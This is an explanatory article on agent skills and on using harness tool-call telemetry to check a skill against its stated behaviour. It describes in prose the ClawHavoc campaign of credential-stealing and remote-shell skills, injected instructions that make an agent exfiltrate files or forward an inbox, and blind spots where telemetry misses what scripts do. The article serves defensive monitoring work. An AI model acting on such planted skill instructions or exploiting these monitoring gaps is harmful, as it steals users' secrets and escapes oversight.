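# Tool-Call Telemetry as Security Evidence About AI Agent Skills

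## Agent skills, tool calls and the records they leave

An agent skill is a folder of instructions, metadata and optional scripts that an AI agent loads for a particular kind of task, such as filling in a PDF form. The agent consists of a language model and a program called the harness, which reads files, runs commands and contacts other services on the model's behalf. People publish skills for strangers to install, much as programmers publish code packages, and each skill comes with its author's statement of what it does. While the agent works, the harness can record the actions the model requests, producing what is called tool-call telemetry. A security team can compare these records with the author's statement to look for mismatches. How much the team learns depends on what the records contain and how precise the statement is.

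Anthropic introduced the Agent Skills format in *Equipping agents for the real world with Agent Skills* (2025) and published it as an open standard on 18 December 2025. Help Net Security's *Malicious AI agent skills can slip past the scanners* reports that one marketplace listed more than 40,000 skills within months, most of them unvetted community contributions.

### What a skill folder holds

The *Specification* of the Agent Skills open standard defines a skill as a directory whose only required file is `SKILL.md`. That file starts with a short block of metadata in YAML, a plain-text format of named fields, followed by instructions in ordinary prose, on which the standard places no format restrictions. The skill's author may add a `scripts/` folder of executable code, a `references/` folder of further documentation, an `assets/` folder of templates and data, and any other files.

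Agents load a skill in stages to save room in the context, the text available to the model when it answers. At startup, the agent loads the name and description of every installed skill, which takes about 100 tokens (word fragments) per skill. It loads the body of `SKILL.md` when it selects the skill for a task, and the other files only if the task requires them. The agent can run a script through the command shell without loading its code into the context. Only the script's output then reaches the model, according to Anthropic's platform documentation.

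Anthropic's *Extend Claude with skills*, the manual page for the coding agent Claude Code, explains that a loaded skill's text stays in the conversation across later turns. The skill may therefore still influence a command that the agent runs hours after loading it.

A skill has no account or permissions of its own. Its instructions are added to the model's context as text, and its scripts normally run as processes under the agent's user account. According to Help Net Security, a skill can therefore reach whatever the agent can: files, credentials, package managers, terminals and outside services. Unit 42, the threat research group of Palo Alto Networks, writes that installing a skill hands over complete control of the agent's identity. That is too strong if the harness asks the user before each command, but about right otherwise.

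### The path of one tool call

Suppose a user asks Claude to fill in a PDF form. The steps below follow Anthropic's own example, with the harness's actions spelled out.

1. The harness assembles its standing instructions, the names and descriptions of the installed skills, and the user's message. It sends this text to the model, usually over the network to the company that hosts it.
2. The model matches the request with the description of a PDF skill and replies with a tool call: a structured request that consists of a tool name and arguments. Here the tool is Bash, the command shell, and the argument is a command that prints `pdf/SKILL.md`.
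3. The harness decides whether to allow the call, by its rules or by asking the user, and then executes it. It carries out some tools itself and passes others to an MCP server, a separate program that offers tools through the Model Context Protocol.
4. The harness adds the output to the conversation and sends the longer conversation back to the model.
5. The model requests the next thing it needs. In the PDF case it reads a second file, `forms.md`, and it can run a Python script from the skill folder that extracts the form's fields. The loop goes on until the model replies with an answer for the user and no further tool call.

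The model never touches the disk. It can only make requests, and the harness does the rest.

The call that runs the Python script looks quite different depending on whether an observer watches it from the network, the harness or the operating system.

A network proxy sits between the machine and everything outside it. An observer who can decrypt the traffic to the model's host can read the whole conversation, including tool requests and results. The proxy also handles any connection that a script opens itself, so its log can show the destination, time and volume. If the script reads a file but none of the contents leave the machine, the proxy has no record of the read.

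The harness handles both the model's request and its execution, so it can record when the model called Bash, whether the user approved, whether the command succeeded and, depending on the settings, what the command was. If the command runs a script, the harness records only a single call. For a script that opened forty files and printed one line, the harness ran one command and received one line of output.

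The operating system handles each of those forty files, every process the script starts and every connection it makes. But it has no representation of prompts or skills, so when Python opens a file, the event looks the same whether a skill, the user or a scheduled job caused it.

Some actions happen without a model request, so a log of only the model's requests would miss them. In Claude Code, a skill's author can put a shell command in `SKILL.md` with an exclamation mark before it. The harness runs the command and inserts its output before the model receives the text. Anthropic states that these commands never prompt the user while the skill loads. Claude Code checks them against the permission rules, but the skill's own metadata can approve them unless the user or the organisation has set a stricter rule.

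### What a skill declares

Declared behaviour is the author's account, in a skill's metadata and description, of what the skill will read, write, run or contact. The current Agent Skills standard gives authors six metadata fields for declaring it.

| Field | Required | Content | Effect on what the skill can do |
| - | - | - | - |
| `name` | Yes | Up to 64 characters, identical to the folder name | None |
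| `description` | Yes | Up to 1,024 characters on what the skill does and when to use it | None; the agent uses it to choose a skill |
| `license` | No | A licence name or a pointer to a licence file | None |
| `compatibility` | No | Up to 500 characters on required products, packages or network access | None |
| `metadata` | No | Any further keys and values | None in the standard |
| `allowed-tools` | No | A list of pre-approved tools, still experimental | Can remove permission prompts |

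The last field, `allowed-tools`, has a misleading name. In Claude Code it lets the agent use the listed tools without asking, but it doesn't block the others. Anthropic states that "every tool remains callable", so a skill with `allowed-tools: Read` is not limited to reading. Claude Code honours the field even in an automated run inside a folder that the user has never marked as trusted, and Anthropic warns that a skill can grant itself broad access this way. Another Claude Code field, `disallowed-tools`, removes tools until the user's next message, but it is not part of the open standard, and a dishonest skill author can leave it out.

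No field limits which files a skill may open or which hosts it may contact. An author can state in the description or under `compatibility` that a skill stays offline, but Claude Code accepts the statement without enforcing it. If the author invents a line such as `network: none`, Claude Code ignores it without an error message, while an upload to claude.ai fails because the field is unknown. The day after the standard came out, the programmer Simon Willison called it "quite heavily under-specified" and pointed to the `metadata` and `allowed-tools` fields in particular (Willison, 2025).

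Researchers sometimes describe skills as having more structure than the open standard gives them. *Agent Skill Security* (Badhe and Tiwari, 2026) defines a skill as a set (*M*, *W*, *P*, *T*, *V*): its descriptive metadata, its workflow, the permissions it requires, the tools it calls, and its provenance and version. The paper lists "permission deception" as an attack in which a skill's author declares fewer permissions than the workflow needs. The open standard has no equivalent of *P*, so a deceptive author has no permission list to falsify and only has to write a misleading sentence or leave one out.

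That leaves prose as the main thing to check, and software is poor at checking prose. *From Skill Text to Skill Structure* (Liang, Wang and colleagues, 2026) compiled 252 skills labeled for six kinds of risk and tested whether a language model could recover the labels. Given the complete `SKILL.md`, the model reached a macro F1 score of 0.409, where 1 would mean no missed and no false findings in any category. Adding a structured digest of each skill's steps and resources raised the score to 0.509, which is still weak support for a security decision.

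A skill's description, however clear, is only its author's claim about what the skill does. In *Agent Skill Supply Chain Risks*, ramimac writes, "Skill metadata is just a label," and cites a warning in Anthropic's documentation that a malicious skill can make Claude act in ways that don't match the skill's stated purpose.

### ClawHavoc

That warning came true in early 2026 on ClawHub, a marketplace for OpenClaw, which The Hacker News (2026) describes as a self-hosted AI assistant. Anyone with a GitHub account at least one week old could publish there. Antiy CERT's *ClawHavoc*, a report from the response team of a Chinese antivirus company, dates the first malicious skill to 27 January. On 31 January, seven attackers released 386 malicious skills. The next day, the firm Koi Security disclosed the campaign and named it ClawHavoc.

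Koi Security (2026) audited all 2,857 skills then on ClawHub and judged 341 malicious, 335 of them part of a single campaign. Later totals vary with the counting method. Antiy CERT counted 1,184 malicious packages by 5 February, including ones that ClawHub had already removed, and traced 1,067 of them to two accounts. Koi's count had reached 824 by 16 February, when the marketplace held more than 10,700 skills.

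Most of these skills relied on their documentation to get malware installed. The text looked professional, and a section headed "Prerequisites" told the reader to install a helper program first. Windows users got a password-protected archive, which antivirus software can't open. Mac users got a script to paste into the Terminal. The script downloaded Atomic Stealer, a program that thieves rent by the month to copy browser data, keychain passwords, SSH keys and cryptocurrency wallets.

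Whether the harness recorded the script depends on who ran it. If the agent read the section and ran the command itself, there would be a tool call, perhaps with the full command in it, but a person pasting the command into a terminal would leave no tool call to record. Help Net Security writes that the instruction files contained directions for the agent to fetch the stealer. However, the text that Koi reproduces is written for a human reader, and Antiy CERT also describes a deception of users. The human version is better supported, though an agent with shell access could have followed the same instructions. The harness may therefore have no record of much of the best-known attack on a skill marketplace.

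A few of the other skills hid their attack in code. Two of them, `better-polymarket` and `polymarket-all-in-one`, searched a prediction market as advertised, but an extra command around line 180 of the script contacted the attacker's server and opened a remote shell, which gave the attacker a command line on the victim's machine. Another skill, `rankaj`, posed as a weather tool. It read the file in which OpenClaw keeps the user's keys to paid AI services and posted the contents to a public web address. In both cases, an agent that ran the script would leave an ordinary market search or weather query in the harness's log. The attack happened inside the script, so only operating system or network records could show it directly. Scanning a skill's files before installation also helps, although attackers can disguise code to get past scanners.

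### The meeting-notes skill

An invented example makes the comparison easier to follow than malware does. The skill `meeting-notes` has a `SKILL.md` that begins like this:

```yaml
---
name: meeting-notes
description: Reads the meeting notes in notes/ and writes one summary to summary.md. Uses no network. Use when the user asks for a summary of meetings.
compatibility: Requires Python 3. No network access needed.
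allowed-tools: Read Write Bash(python3:*)
---
```

The folder also holds one script, `scripts/collect.py`, which joins the notes in date order so that the model can summarise them. The skill's declared behaviour is to read the files in `notes/`, run Python, write the single file `summary.md` and make no network connections. Any other action is undeclared, such as the script opening the user's SSH keys, a second output file appearing, or the machine connecting to an unfamiliar host while the script runs. An undeclared action is not necessarily malicious. The script might connect to a host to check for updates, for example, and the author might have forgotten to mention it.

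No line in that block enforces the promise. Only the last line has any force, and it permits more than was promised, because `Bash(python3:*)` approves every Python command in advance, including one that sends the notes to a server.

People disagree about how to test such a declaration. Some would start with the agent's own records, comparing the tool calls with the declaration and investigating any mismatch. Others argue that these records miss too much of what scripts do, so defenders must also monitor the operating system. Others would settle the question before installation by running the skill in a sandbox, an isolated environment where a theft does no harm. Some object on privacy grounds that detailed records capture prompts, file contents and secrets, and argue that organisations should collect less. Across all these positions, people also dispute whether anyone can attribute an observed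 action to a particular skill when several skills and the user's own request share one context, and what such records have contributed to real investigations so far.

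## What a tool-call record contains

To compare `meeting-notes` with its declaration, a security team needs records of which command ran and which file the agent wrote. Harnesses differ a lot in how much of this they export. Claude Code is the main example here because Anthropic's *Monitoring* documents its records field by field. Claude Code exports them through OpenTelemetry, an open-source project that defines common formats for reporting what software does. A server called a collector receives the records and forwards them to the organisation's database or security system.

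A tool call that goes ahead produces two events. Claude Code logs `tool_decision` when a rule or a person allows or refuses the call, and `tool_result` when the tool finishes. A refused call produces only `tool_decision`.

### The fields of a record

`tool_name` is the name of the tool that the model requested, such as Read, Write or Bash. It distinguishes a file read from a shell command, but every shell command run through Bash is recorded as Bash. Tools from user-added MCP servers are recorded by default under the placeholder `mcp_tool`, so a calendar lookup and a database deletion get the same value.

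Each tool call has a unique `tool_use_id`, which appears on both events and in the data that Claude Code passes to hooks. Hooks are programs that an organisation or a user can set to run before or after a tool call. The ID also matches an entry in the session transcript on the user's disk, so an investigator who finds a suspicious event may be able to look up the conversation around it if the transcript still exists. Claude Code deletes transcripts after 30 days by default, and Anthropic warns that their format can change with any release.

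`session.id` groups all events in a session, and `prompt.id` groups the events between one user prompt and the next. Filtering by `prompt.id` therefore shows what the agent did after a given request, but a skill loaded under an earlier prompt can still influence those actions. If the user signed in with a Claude account, each event also includes their email address and account identifiers. If they used a direct API key or a cloud platform such as Amazon Bedrock, those fields are missing, which leaves only the session identifier and a random installation identifier. The organisation then has to add the user's name itself.

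`event.timestamp` records when the event occurred, and `duration_ms` records how long the tool ran. Since Claude Code logs `tool_result` when the tool finishes, subtracting the duration from the timestamp gives the tool's approximate start time. An analyst needs that window to find activity from the same period in a network or operating system log.

The permission decision is either `accept` or `reject`, and a second field gives its source:

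- `user_temporary`: the user chose "Yes" at a prompt, for one call or, with some file prompts, for the rest of the session.
- `user_permanent`: the user chose "Yes" and asked not to see the prompt again.
- `user_reject` and `user_abort`: the user chose "No" or dismissed the prompt.
- `hook`: a hook returned the decision.
- `config`: Claude Code decided without asking anyone.

In a normal interactive session, later calls under a saved approval have the source `config`. In an automated session they keep the value `user_permanent`, so that value doesn't prove that a person was present. The vaguest value is `config`, which covers project settings, personal rules, company policy, command-line options and tools that Claude Code treats as inherently safe. The event doesn't show which of these applied. Anthropic's list of causes for `config` leaves out a skill's own `allowed-tools` line, but no other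 value fits a call approved by that line, so such calls probably appear as `config` too. If they do, a command that a skill approved for itself looks the same in the log as one that the company's administrators approved.

`success` is true or false, and a failed call also has an error category such as `Error:ENOENT`, the code for a missing file. The field records whether the tool ran without error, even if it harms the user, so a script that copies a private key and exits normally counts as a success.

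Claude Code also records the size of the input and the result in bytes. The result is only what the harness receives back from the tool, so a script can do a lot and still have a small result size.

Arguments are the most useful field for checking a declaration, but Claude Code leaves them out by default. An administrator can include them by setting `OTEL_LOG_TOOL_DETAILS=1`, which records them in two forms. `tool_parameters` holds selected values, including the full text of a shell command and whether the call asked to run outside Claude Code's sandbox. `tool_input` holds the arguments of any tool, but Claude Code shortens each value over 512 characters and limits the total to about 4,000 characters. This can cut off the end of a long web address, where stolen data might be.

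The arguments on the two events can differ, because the permission step can rewrite a call while approving it. When they do, the version on `tool_result` is the better guide to what ran. Anthropic states that events contain no raw file contents, but also that `tool_input` holds the tool's arguments, which for Write would normally include the text of the new file. An organisation that turns on tool details should check whether its own events include that text.

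Neither of these two events includes the tool's output. An administrator can capture it by turning on tracing, a beta feature, and setting `OTEL_LOG_TOOL_CONTENT=1`, which records up to 60 KB each of input and output. Another option is `OTEL_LOG_RAW_API_BODIES`, which exports every model request and response. Each request contains the conversation so far, including earlier tool results.

### The OpenTelemetry conventions

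Most of the names above are Claude Code's own. OpenTelemetry also publishes semantic conventions, which are agreed names and meanings for fields, so that records from different products can share one database. Greptime, a database company, reports in *How OpenTelemetry Traces LLM Calls, Agent Reasoning, and MCP Tools* (2026) that OpenTelemetry formed its generative AI working group in April 2024 to standardise records of calls to models. Later, version 1.38 added tool definitions and call details, 1.39 added conventions for MCP, and 1.41 required the tool's name in the title of each tool record.

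The basic unit in these conventions is the span, a record of one operation with a start time, an end time and a set of attributes. Spans nest inside one another to form a trace, so a trace of one user request can contain a span for each model call and each tool call. OpenTelemetry's *Semantic conventions for generative client AI spans* defines eight attributes for the execute-tool span:

| Attribute | Requirement level | Content |
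| - | - | - |
| `gen_ai.operation.name` | Required | The value `execute_tool` |
| `error.type` | Required if the call failed | Class of error |
| `gen_ai.tool.name` | Recommended | Name of the tool |
| `gen_ai.tool.call.id` | Recommended if available | Identifier of the call |
| `gen_ai.tool.description` | Recommended if available | Description of the tool |
| `gen_ai.tool.type` | Recommended if available | Function, extension or datastore |
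| `gen_ai.tool.call.arguments` | Opt-in | Parameters of the call |
| `gen_ai.tool.call.result` | Opt-in | What the tool returned |

The two opt-in attributes carry a warning about sensitive information. Only these two would show whether a skill stayed within its declaration, but a product can follow the conventions fully without recording either.

The table has no attribute for the permission decision, for input and result sizes, or for the skill in use. Vendors can add such attributes, but each picks its own names. Claude Code's tool spans carry both `gen_ai.tool.call.id` and its own `tool_use_id`, with the same value. Its model spans still use `gen_ai.system`, which OpenTelemetry replaced in version 1.37. A team that monitors several agents will have to translate between the different names.

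For MCP tools, the conventions define one span on the agent's side and another on the server's. If both sides pass along the trace identifier, the server's span nests under the agent's, and an analyst can compare the request with what the server recorded. Otherwise, the two spans end up in separate traces.

Version 1.41 was the last numbered series of the main conventions to contain these definitions. *OpenTelemetry GenAI Conventions* (Wang, 2026) explains that version 1.42.0 moved them to a separate repository in June 2026, and OpenTelemetry's *Moved* confirms that OpenTelemetry no longer maintains the old page. The new repository had no official release by 21 August 2026. Its conventions have the status "Development", so names and structures may still change. A detection rule built on them should specify the version it was written for.

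### Defaults in Claude Code, Cowork and Codex

Three widely used agents show how far the defaults differ. Claude Cowork is Anthropic's agent for office work, and Codex is OpenAI's coding agent. Anthropic documents Cowork's events in a reference page and a help article, *Monitor Claude Cowork activity with OpenTelemetry*. OpenAI's *Advanced Configuration* covers where users may set Codex's telemetry options, but the table's details about Codex events come from *Codex CLI Observability*, by the independent blogger Vaughan (2026), and a developer's note in the Codex source code. The Codex column therefore rests on weaker evidence than the other two.

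| | Claude Code | Claude Cowork | Codex |
| - | - | - | - |
| Export begins when | Someone turns on telemetry and chooses an exporter | An administrator enters a collector address | Someone configures an exporter |
| Tool events by default | Tool name, identifiers, time, duration, decision, success, sizes | Tool name, duration, decision, success, paths of connected folders | Tool name, duration, decision, success, arguments, output |
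| Prompt text | Needs `OTEL_LOG_USER_PROMPTS` | Needs `userPrompts` | Needs `log_user_prompt` |
| Tool arguments | Need `OTEL_LOG_TOOL_DETAILS` | Need `toolDetails` | On |
| Skill names | Partly masked without tool details | Placeholder for skills from outside Anthropic without `toolDetails` | No skill event in Vaughan's list |
| Tool results | Only in traces or raw API bodies, each with its own switch | Not part of `toolDetails`, except error messages | Excerpt of the output |

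Codex is the outlier. Lin explains in the source-code note *feat(otel): safe tracing* that OpenAI uses the log export for its own security monitoring and keeps it "intentionally content-rich", including tool arguments and outputs. Vaughan (2026), in *Codex CLI OpenTelemetry*, warns that even with prompt logging turned off, Codex still exports tool results, which can contain the contents of sensitive files.

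Traces from Codex contain much less detail. A copy of a Codex change description on letscooking.netlify.app lists what OpenAI removed from them, including raw arguments, raw output, account identity and the events for permission decisions. Claude Code does the reverse, making tool output available in traces but not in ordinary tool events. Its traces also include the permission decision and its source. A team that collected only traces could therefore have a call's permission decision and output from Claude Code, but neither from Codex.

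Cowork's content setting, `otlpContentCapture`, applies only to sessions that users start from the desktop app. Sessions that begin on the web or on a phone, and scheduled tasks in the cloud, export only metadata. If a skill misbehaves in a scheduled cloud task, the exported events won't contain its commands. Some older desktop versions send prompts, responses and tool arguments even when nobody has configured the setting. Cowork also exports the user's email address and API error messages regardless of the setting.

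In Cowork's Auto mode, a classifier decides whether a call may go ahead, and the event adds a `classifier_verdict`, such as `allow` or `block`, next to the source `config`. Analysts can use this field to tell a classifier's approval from an ordinary rule's.

### Skill and plugin events

Besides tool calls, Claude Code logs a `skill_activated` event each time the model invokes a skill through the Skill tool or the user runs it as a slash command. One field shows whether the model, the user or another skill triggered it. Another shows where the skill came from, such as the user's personal settings, the project folder or a plugin. Claude Code records the name of any skill written by the user or a third party as `custom_skill`, unless the administrator has turned on tool details.

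The same name can still appear elsewhere in the default export. Claude Code attaches the active skill's name to its `api_request` events, which record calls to the model. It gives the names of user-defined skills in full and masks only those from third-party plugins. A folder that someone downloads from a marketplace and copies into their personal skills directory presumably counts as user-defined. A team with default settings could therefore find the name `meeting-notes` on the model requests but not on the activation event.

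The `tool_result` and `tool_decision` events have no field for the active skill. Only the call that loads a skill identifies it in its arguments, so linking later calls to that skill requires inference.

Skills often come in plugins, packages that can also contain hooks and MCP servers. Claude Code logs `plugin_installed` when a user installs a plugin and `plugin_loaded` for each enabled plugin at the start of a session. The `plugin_loaded` event gives the number of skill directories and whether the plugin adds hooks or MCP servers. Third-party names are masked here too, but a hash of the plugin's name and marketplace remains, and it is always the same for a given plugin. A security team could get a suspect plugin's hash by loading it on a test machine in safe mode, where Claude Code reports the plugin without running any of its parts, and then search the company's records for that hash.

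Anthropic lists no comparable event for installing a plain skill folder. Someone can copy a folder into place, and the first record may come only when the agent activates the skill. There is also no separate event for the shell commands that Claude Code runs while it loads a skill's text, so an administrator would have to test whether those commands leave a record.

### Gaps in collection

None of the three products exports records until someone configures it to. Claude Code needs at least two settings, one to enable telemetry and one to choose an exporter, plus a protocol setting if the records go to a collector. Recording starts only then, so a company that turns on telemetry after an incident can't recover the events it missed, although transcripts on users' machines may help.

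Export can fail without the user noticing, because Claude Code writes export errors to its debug log, which few people read during normal work. Versions 2.1.191 to 2.1.211, for example, sent records over HTTP without stating their length, and Azure Monitor, Microsoft's monitoring service, rejected them. In the collected data, a broken exporter looks the same as an idle user. Anthropic suggests submitting a prompt and checking whether a `user_prompt` event arrives. It would make sense to repeat this check after every update.

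Sessions can be missing even when the exporter works. Claude Code labels terminal sessions `claude-code` and sessions from the desktop app's Code tab `claude-code-desktop`, so a dashboard that filters on the first label omits the desktop sessions. Cowork runs in the same desktop app, but its collector settings don't apply to the Code tab.

Developers can also change what the company receives. Administrators can fix the collector's address through managed settings, which override a developer's own. If they fix only the address, a developer can still switch off an exporter or send its output to the screen. A malicious script running under the developer's account could presumably edit the same settings. Codex ignores telemetry options in a project's own configuration file, so a downloaded project can't redirect the records that way.

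Claude Code withholds environment variables whose names begin with `OTEL_`, including its exporter settings, from the shell commands, hooks, MCP servers and language servers it starts. Even if `collect.py` contained its own OpenTelemetry code, it wouldn't send anything to the company's collector unless someone supplied the address separately. Withholding the settings also protects the collector's password, which they often include. When tracing is on, shell commands do receive the identifier of the current trace. A program can use it to link its own records to the agent's, though an attacker would have no reason to do this.

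`event.sequence` can't reliably order events in a resumed session. Claude Code resets it to zero each time the program starts and adds one for each event. A resumed session keeps its `session.id` but restarts the count, so a later event can have the same number as an earlier one, or a lower number. Cowork's numbering restarts in the same way. An analyst who sorts by number alone could place a file write before the command that produced its contents. Anthropic recommends sorting by timestamp and using the sequence number only to order events with the same timestamp.

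### A three-call record of the meeting-notes skill

Suppose a user asks Claude Code to summarise the week's meetings. The invented record below shows the three `tool_result` events, shortened, with tool details turned on. A plus sign marks the fields that are missing by default. All three calls share one session and one prompt identifier.

```text
Call 1
  tool_name=Skill  tool_use_id=t-01  event.sequence=14
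  event.timestamp=10:02:07.310  duration_ms=12  success=true
  decision_source=user_temporary
  tool_input_size_bytes=25  tool_result_size_bytes=60
+ skill_name=meeting-notes

Call 2
  tool_name=Bash  tool_use_id=t-02  event.sequence=17
  event.timestamp=10:02:15.420  duration_ms=1940  success=true
  decision_source=config
  tool_input_size_bytes=78  tool_result_size_bytes=48210
+ full_command=python3 ~/.claude/skills/meeting-notes/scripts/collect.py notes/

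Call 3
  tool_name=Write  tool_use_id=t-03  event.sequence=20
  event.timestamp=10:02:31.905  duration_ms=18  success=true
  decision_source=config
  tool_input_size_bytes=2310  tool_result_size_bytes=64
+ file_path=/home/ana/team/summary.md
```

The sequence numbers skip because other events, such as permission decisions and model requests, fall between the calls.

Call 1 is evidence that the agent loaded a skill named `meeting-notes` and that the user approved it. It is weaker evidence of which text the agent loaded, because the event has no version number or hash for the skill. If its author had changed `SKILL.md` the day before, this record would look the same.

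Call 2 is evidence that the harness ran the skill's script with `notes/` as its argument, which fits the declaration. The script started at about 10:02:13.5 and finished two seconds later. It returned 48,210 bytes, a plausible size for a week of notes, which the team could check against the files in the folder. The record doesn't show which files the script opened or whether it contacted a server. No one approved this particular command at a prompt, probably because the skill's own `allowed-tools` line already allowed it, but approval by a personal rule or a company policy would also be recorded as `config`.

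Call 3 is the strongest evidence of the three. The harness carries out Write itself, so the record gives the path of the file it wrote, which matches the one output the skill declares. The record doesn't rule out a second file, since `collect.py` could have written one during call 2.

Under Claude Code's default settings, the same events show that the agent loaded a skill, ran a shell command for two seconds and wrote a file. The team couldn't tell from these events whether the file was `summary.md` or the list of SSH keys allowed to log in to the machine.

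## Checking a skill's declared behaviour against its tool calls

The reason to start with the agent's own records is that the harness sits between the model and everything the model acts on. *Methods for Formal Verification of Agent Skills* (2026) makes only one structural assumption about the harness, which is that it can intercept each call before execution. A security team can use that interception point to record calls and to stop any call that doesn't fit the skill's declaration.

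Tool-call records are also easy to compare with a declaration because both describe the same kinds of things. The declaration for `meeting-notes` lists a folder and an output file, and the harness can record paths and commands.

Tool-call records are most useful for skills that contain only prose. Wu, Li and Liu (2026), in *Behavioral Integrity Verification for AI Agent Skills*, compared the declarations of 49,943 skills with their contents, and about 45% of the mismatches they found were in skills without code. A code scanner has nothing to parse in such a skill, and what happens depends on how the model interprets the text. But the agent still has to act through tool calls, so the harness can record each step. If the skill tells the agent to download and run a program, however, the program's own actions don't appear as tool calls.

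Telemetry also covers ordinary work, with real files and real requests, so it could plausibly catch harmful actions that a sandbox run misses. *Beyond Maliciousness* (Pandey, Singh and colleagues, 2026) ran about 6,300 skills in a sandbox, most of them once, and notes that a single session exercises few of a skill's code paths. This advantage of monitoring everyday sessions is still unmeasured, and the paper leaves testing it to future work.

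### The declared set and the observed set

The comparison needs a shared list of capabilities. *Formal Analysis and Supply Chain Security for Agentic AI Skills* (2026) defines a capability as a pair, a type of resource and a level of access to it, such as files and read access. Let *D* be the set of capabilities that a skill declares. Let *O* be the set that the records show the agent using while it worked under the skill. Every capability on the list then falls into one of four groups:

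| In *D*? | In *O*? | What follows |
| - | - | - |
| No | Yes | The observation contradicts the declaration |
| Yes | Yes | The observation is consistent with the declaration |
| Yes | No | An unused permission, which proves little |
| No | No | Either the skill didn't use the capability or the records missed it |

Because the records have gaps, the comparison can show that a skill exceeded its declaration but usually can't show that it stayed within it. Let *B* be everything the skill caused in a session. If the records are accurate, *O* is a part of *B*, and rarely all of it. A single capability in *O* but outside *D* is therefore enough to show that *B* goes beyond *D*. If *O* lies entirely inside *D*, *B* may still go beyond *D*, unless coverage is complete and the records could have shown everything the skill did.

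A tool call contradicts a skill's declared behaviour only if the skill caused the call. The user may have asked for the action, or the agent may have done the same thing without the skill. For this reason, *SkillSentry* (2026) compares matched test runs with and without the skill, but attributing a call to a skill is harder in everyday use.

A permission that goes unused in a session is poor evidence that the skill doesn't need it, because a session exercises so little of the skill. In the corpus that Pandey and colleagues studied, half the skills showed evidence that they could run shell commands, but the sandbox runs recorded a shell call for about one skill in twelve. A reviewer who removed shell permission from every skill without a recorded shell call would break many of them.

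Deciding what belongs in *D* takes judgement because few skill authors use the `allowed-tools` field, and the lists they do provide are often incomplete. Pandey and colleagues found the field filled in for 770 of the 6,061 skills with readable metadata, or 12.7%. Of those 770 lists, 59% understated what the skill's files could do and only 22% matched. Shell execution and network access were the most common omissions. The field also has no way to express access to credentials.

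The same study compares *D* and *O* on a small scale. The sandbox runs recorded 91 of the 770 skills using at least one capability that the field can express, and 54 of those 91 used one that the skill's author hadn't listed. That share is high, but most skills had no control run. For those that did, the agent called the shell in every control run, so some of the 54 mismatches may come from the agent rather than the skill. Three of the study's authors work for Metano Labs, which builds the scanner, and nobody outside the company has evaluated the scanner.

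*D* therefore has to come mostly from prose, and a description that omits a behaviour should be treated differently from one that denies it. If a skill connects to the network and its description doesn't mention this, the omission may be an oversight. The description of `meeting-notes` reads "Uses no network", so a connection would make that statement false. *ToolGuardian* (2026) keeps such judgements out of the comparison. It stores each mismatch as a fact, and the organisation's policy then determines whether to reject the tool, restrict it, warn the user or block the call.

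### From tool calls to capabilities

Wu and colleagues sort behaviour into 29 capabilities:

| Family | Capabilities |
| - | - |
| Network | Outbound HTTP, outbound socket, inbound connection, download and execute |
| File system | Read project files, read sensitive files, read home folder, write, write sensitive files, list files, delete |
| Process execution | Run a program, run a shell command, evaluate code, evaluate dynamically built code |
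| Environment | Read one environment variable, read many, read sensitive ones |
| Encoding | Base64, cryptography, compression |
| Credentials | Read, create, transmit |
| Instructions | Override other instructions, conceal actions, take over the agent's identity, act silently, direct the agent to send data out |

A Read call is easy to map because its path shows whether the file belongs to the project, the home folder or a sensitive location. Bash calls are much harder to map. A command that posts a file with `curl` maps to a shell command and outbound HTTP, but `python3 collect.py notes/` maps only to running a program, even if the script sends data. *RuntimeTickets* (2026) also points out this limit.

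Pan, Sun and colleagues (2026), in *SkillGuard*, try to close this gap by reading the script before it runs. Before each tool call, a hook triggers their tool, which maps the call to a capability and looks for it in the skill's manifest, a machine-readable list of permissions. For a shell command, a small read-only agent also reads the command and any script it refers to, then infers what other capabilities they need.

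One SkillGuard test case closely resembles `meeting-notes`. A skill for editing Word documents contained an added instruction to run `file_backup.py`. This looked like a sensible backup step, but the script would have posted the document to an attacker's server. SkillGuard read the script and blocked it because it needed permission to post to the web, which the manifest didn't include.

Pan and colleagues tested 50 skills on three agents. Attacks that blended into the skill's workflow succeeded in 35.3% of runs without SkillGuard and 20.7% with it. For blunter attacks, the rate fell from 36.7% to 18.0%. With SkillGuard, the agents completed 80.6% of legitimate tasks, down from 87.1%, and the whole drop came from Codex. The test setup approved every declared permission automatically, so an attentive user might have stopped more attacks. But two of the paper's authors wrote the manifests after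 studying the safe version of each skill, and skills on public marketplaces don't come with manifests of that quality.

Some of the attacks that got through used only permissions the skill had already declared. In one case, the attacker wrote text instructing an email skill to forward the whole inbox to an outside address. Forwarding needs the same capabilities as normal sending, so *O* stayed inside *D*. The tests in *RuntimeTickets* showed the same weakness, because SkillGuard checked a send's capability but not its destination.

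Adding targets to the list could help a team catch data going to an unfamiliar server. In *Skills as Verifiable Artifacts*, Metere (2026) writes capabilities as `net.egress(host)` or `fs.read(path)`, so a skill can declare one host instead of the whole internet. The team still wouldn't catch the forwarded inbox if the messages left through the usual mail provider, because that host would be declared. The team would have to compare the recipients with the user's request to catch it.

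### The order of calls

A set does not record order, and some attacks consist of permitted actions in a harmful order. Suppose a skill for a cloud service declares that it reads an API key and uses the network, both of which it needs to log in. In a normal session, the agent reads the key and contacts the service. In a theft, it reads the key and sends it somewhere else. Both sessions produce the same *O*, which lies inside *D*.

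*Methods for Formal Verification of Agent Skills* uses a trace, a time-ordered list of the model's tool calls and the effects of the scripts they launch. Each entry records its origin, the capability requested and the permission decision. Claude Code's events can supply only the tool-call part of this trace.

A simple rule flags any outbound call in the trace that comes after the agent has read a secret. The rule should cover the whole session, not only the current prompt, because the secret stays in the conversation and the model can copy it into a command much later. The order of the calls doesn't prove that the secret left the machine. If the team captures both tool results and arguments, it can search the outgoing command for the secret, though base64 encoding defeats a plain text search.

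Wu and colleagues' results give some support for looking at sequences. Their classifier labelled 37% of undeclared network capabilities adversarial. The share was 58% for chains that read data and send it out, 86% for chains that download code and run it, and only 8% for undeclared chains from one file to another. Unit 42's *Trust No Skill*, a summary of the same research, concludes that the threat comes from the chain rather than its individual steps. However, the classifier's rules treat several of these chains as hostile, so part of the difference comes from the rules themselves.

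### Comparing the meeting-notes record

For `meeting-notes`, *D* contains reading files in `notes/`, running Python and writing `summary.md`, and the author explicitly denies network use. *O*, taken from the three-call record with tool details, contains running a program and writing `summary.md`. The script very likely read the notes, but *O* doesn't include that because the reading happened inside the script. Everything in *O* is also in *D*, so the record is consistent with the declaration.

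Small changes to the session show what the comparison can detect:

| What happens instead | Tool-call record, with tool details | Result |
| - | - | - |
| The agent opens the user's SSH key with Read | Read, with the path of the key | Contradiction |
| The agent uploads `summary.md` with `curl` | Bash, with the full command | Contradiction of an explicit denial |
| The agent writes a second file, `notes/index.md` | Write, with the path | Contradiction only if *D* includes targets |
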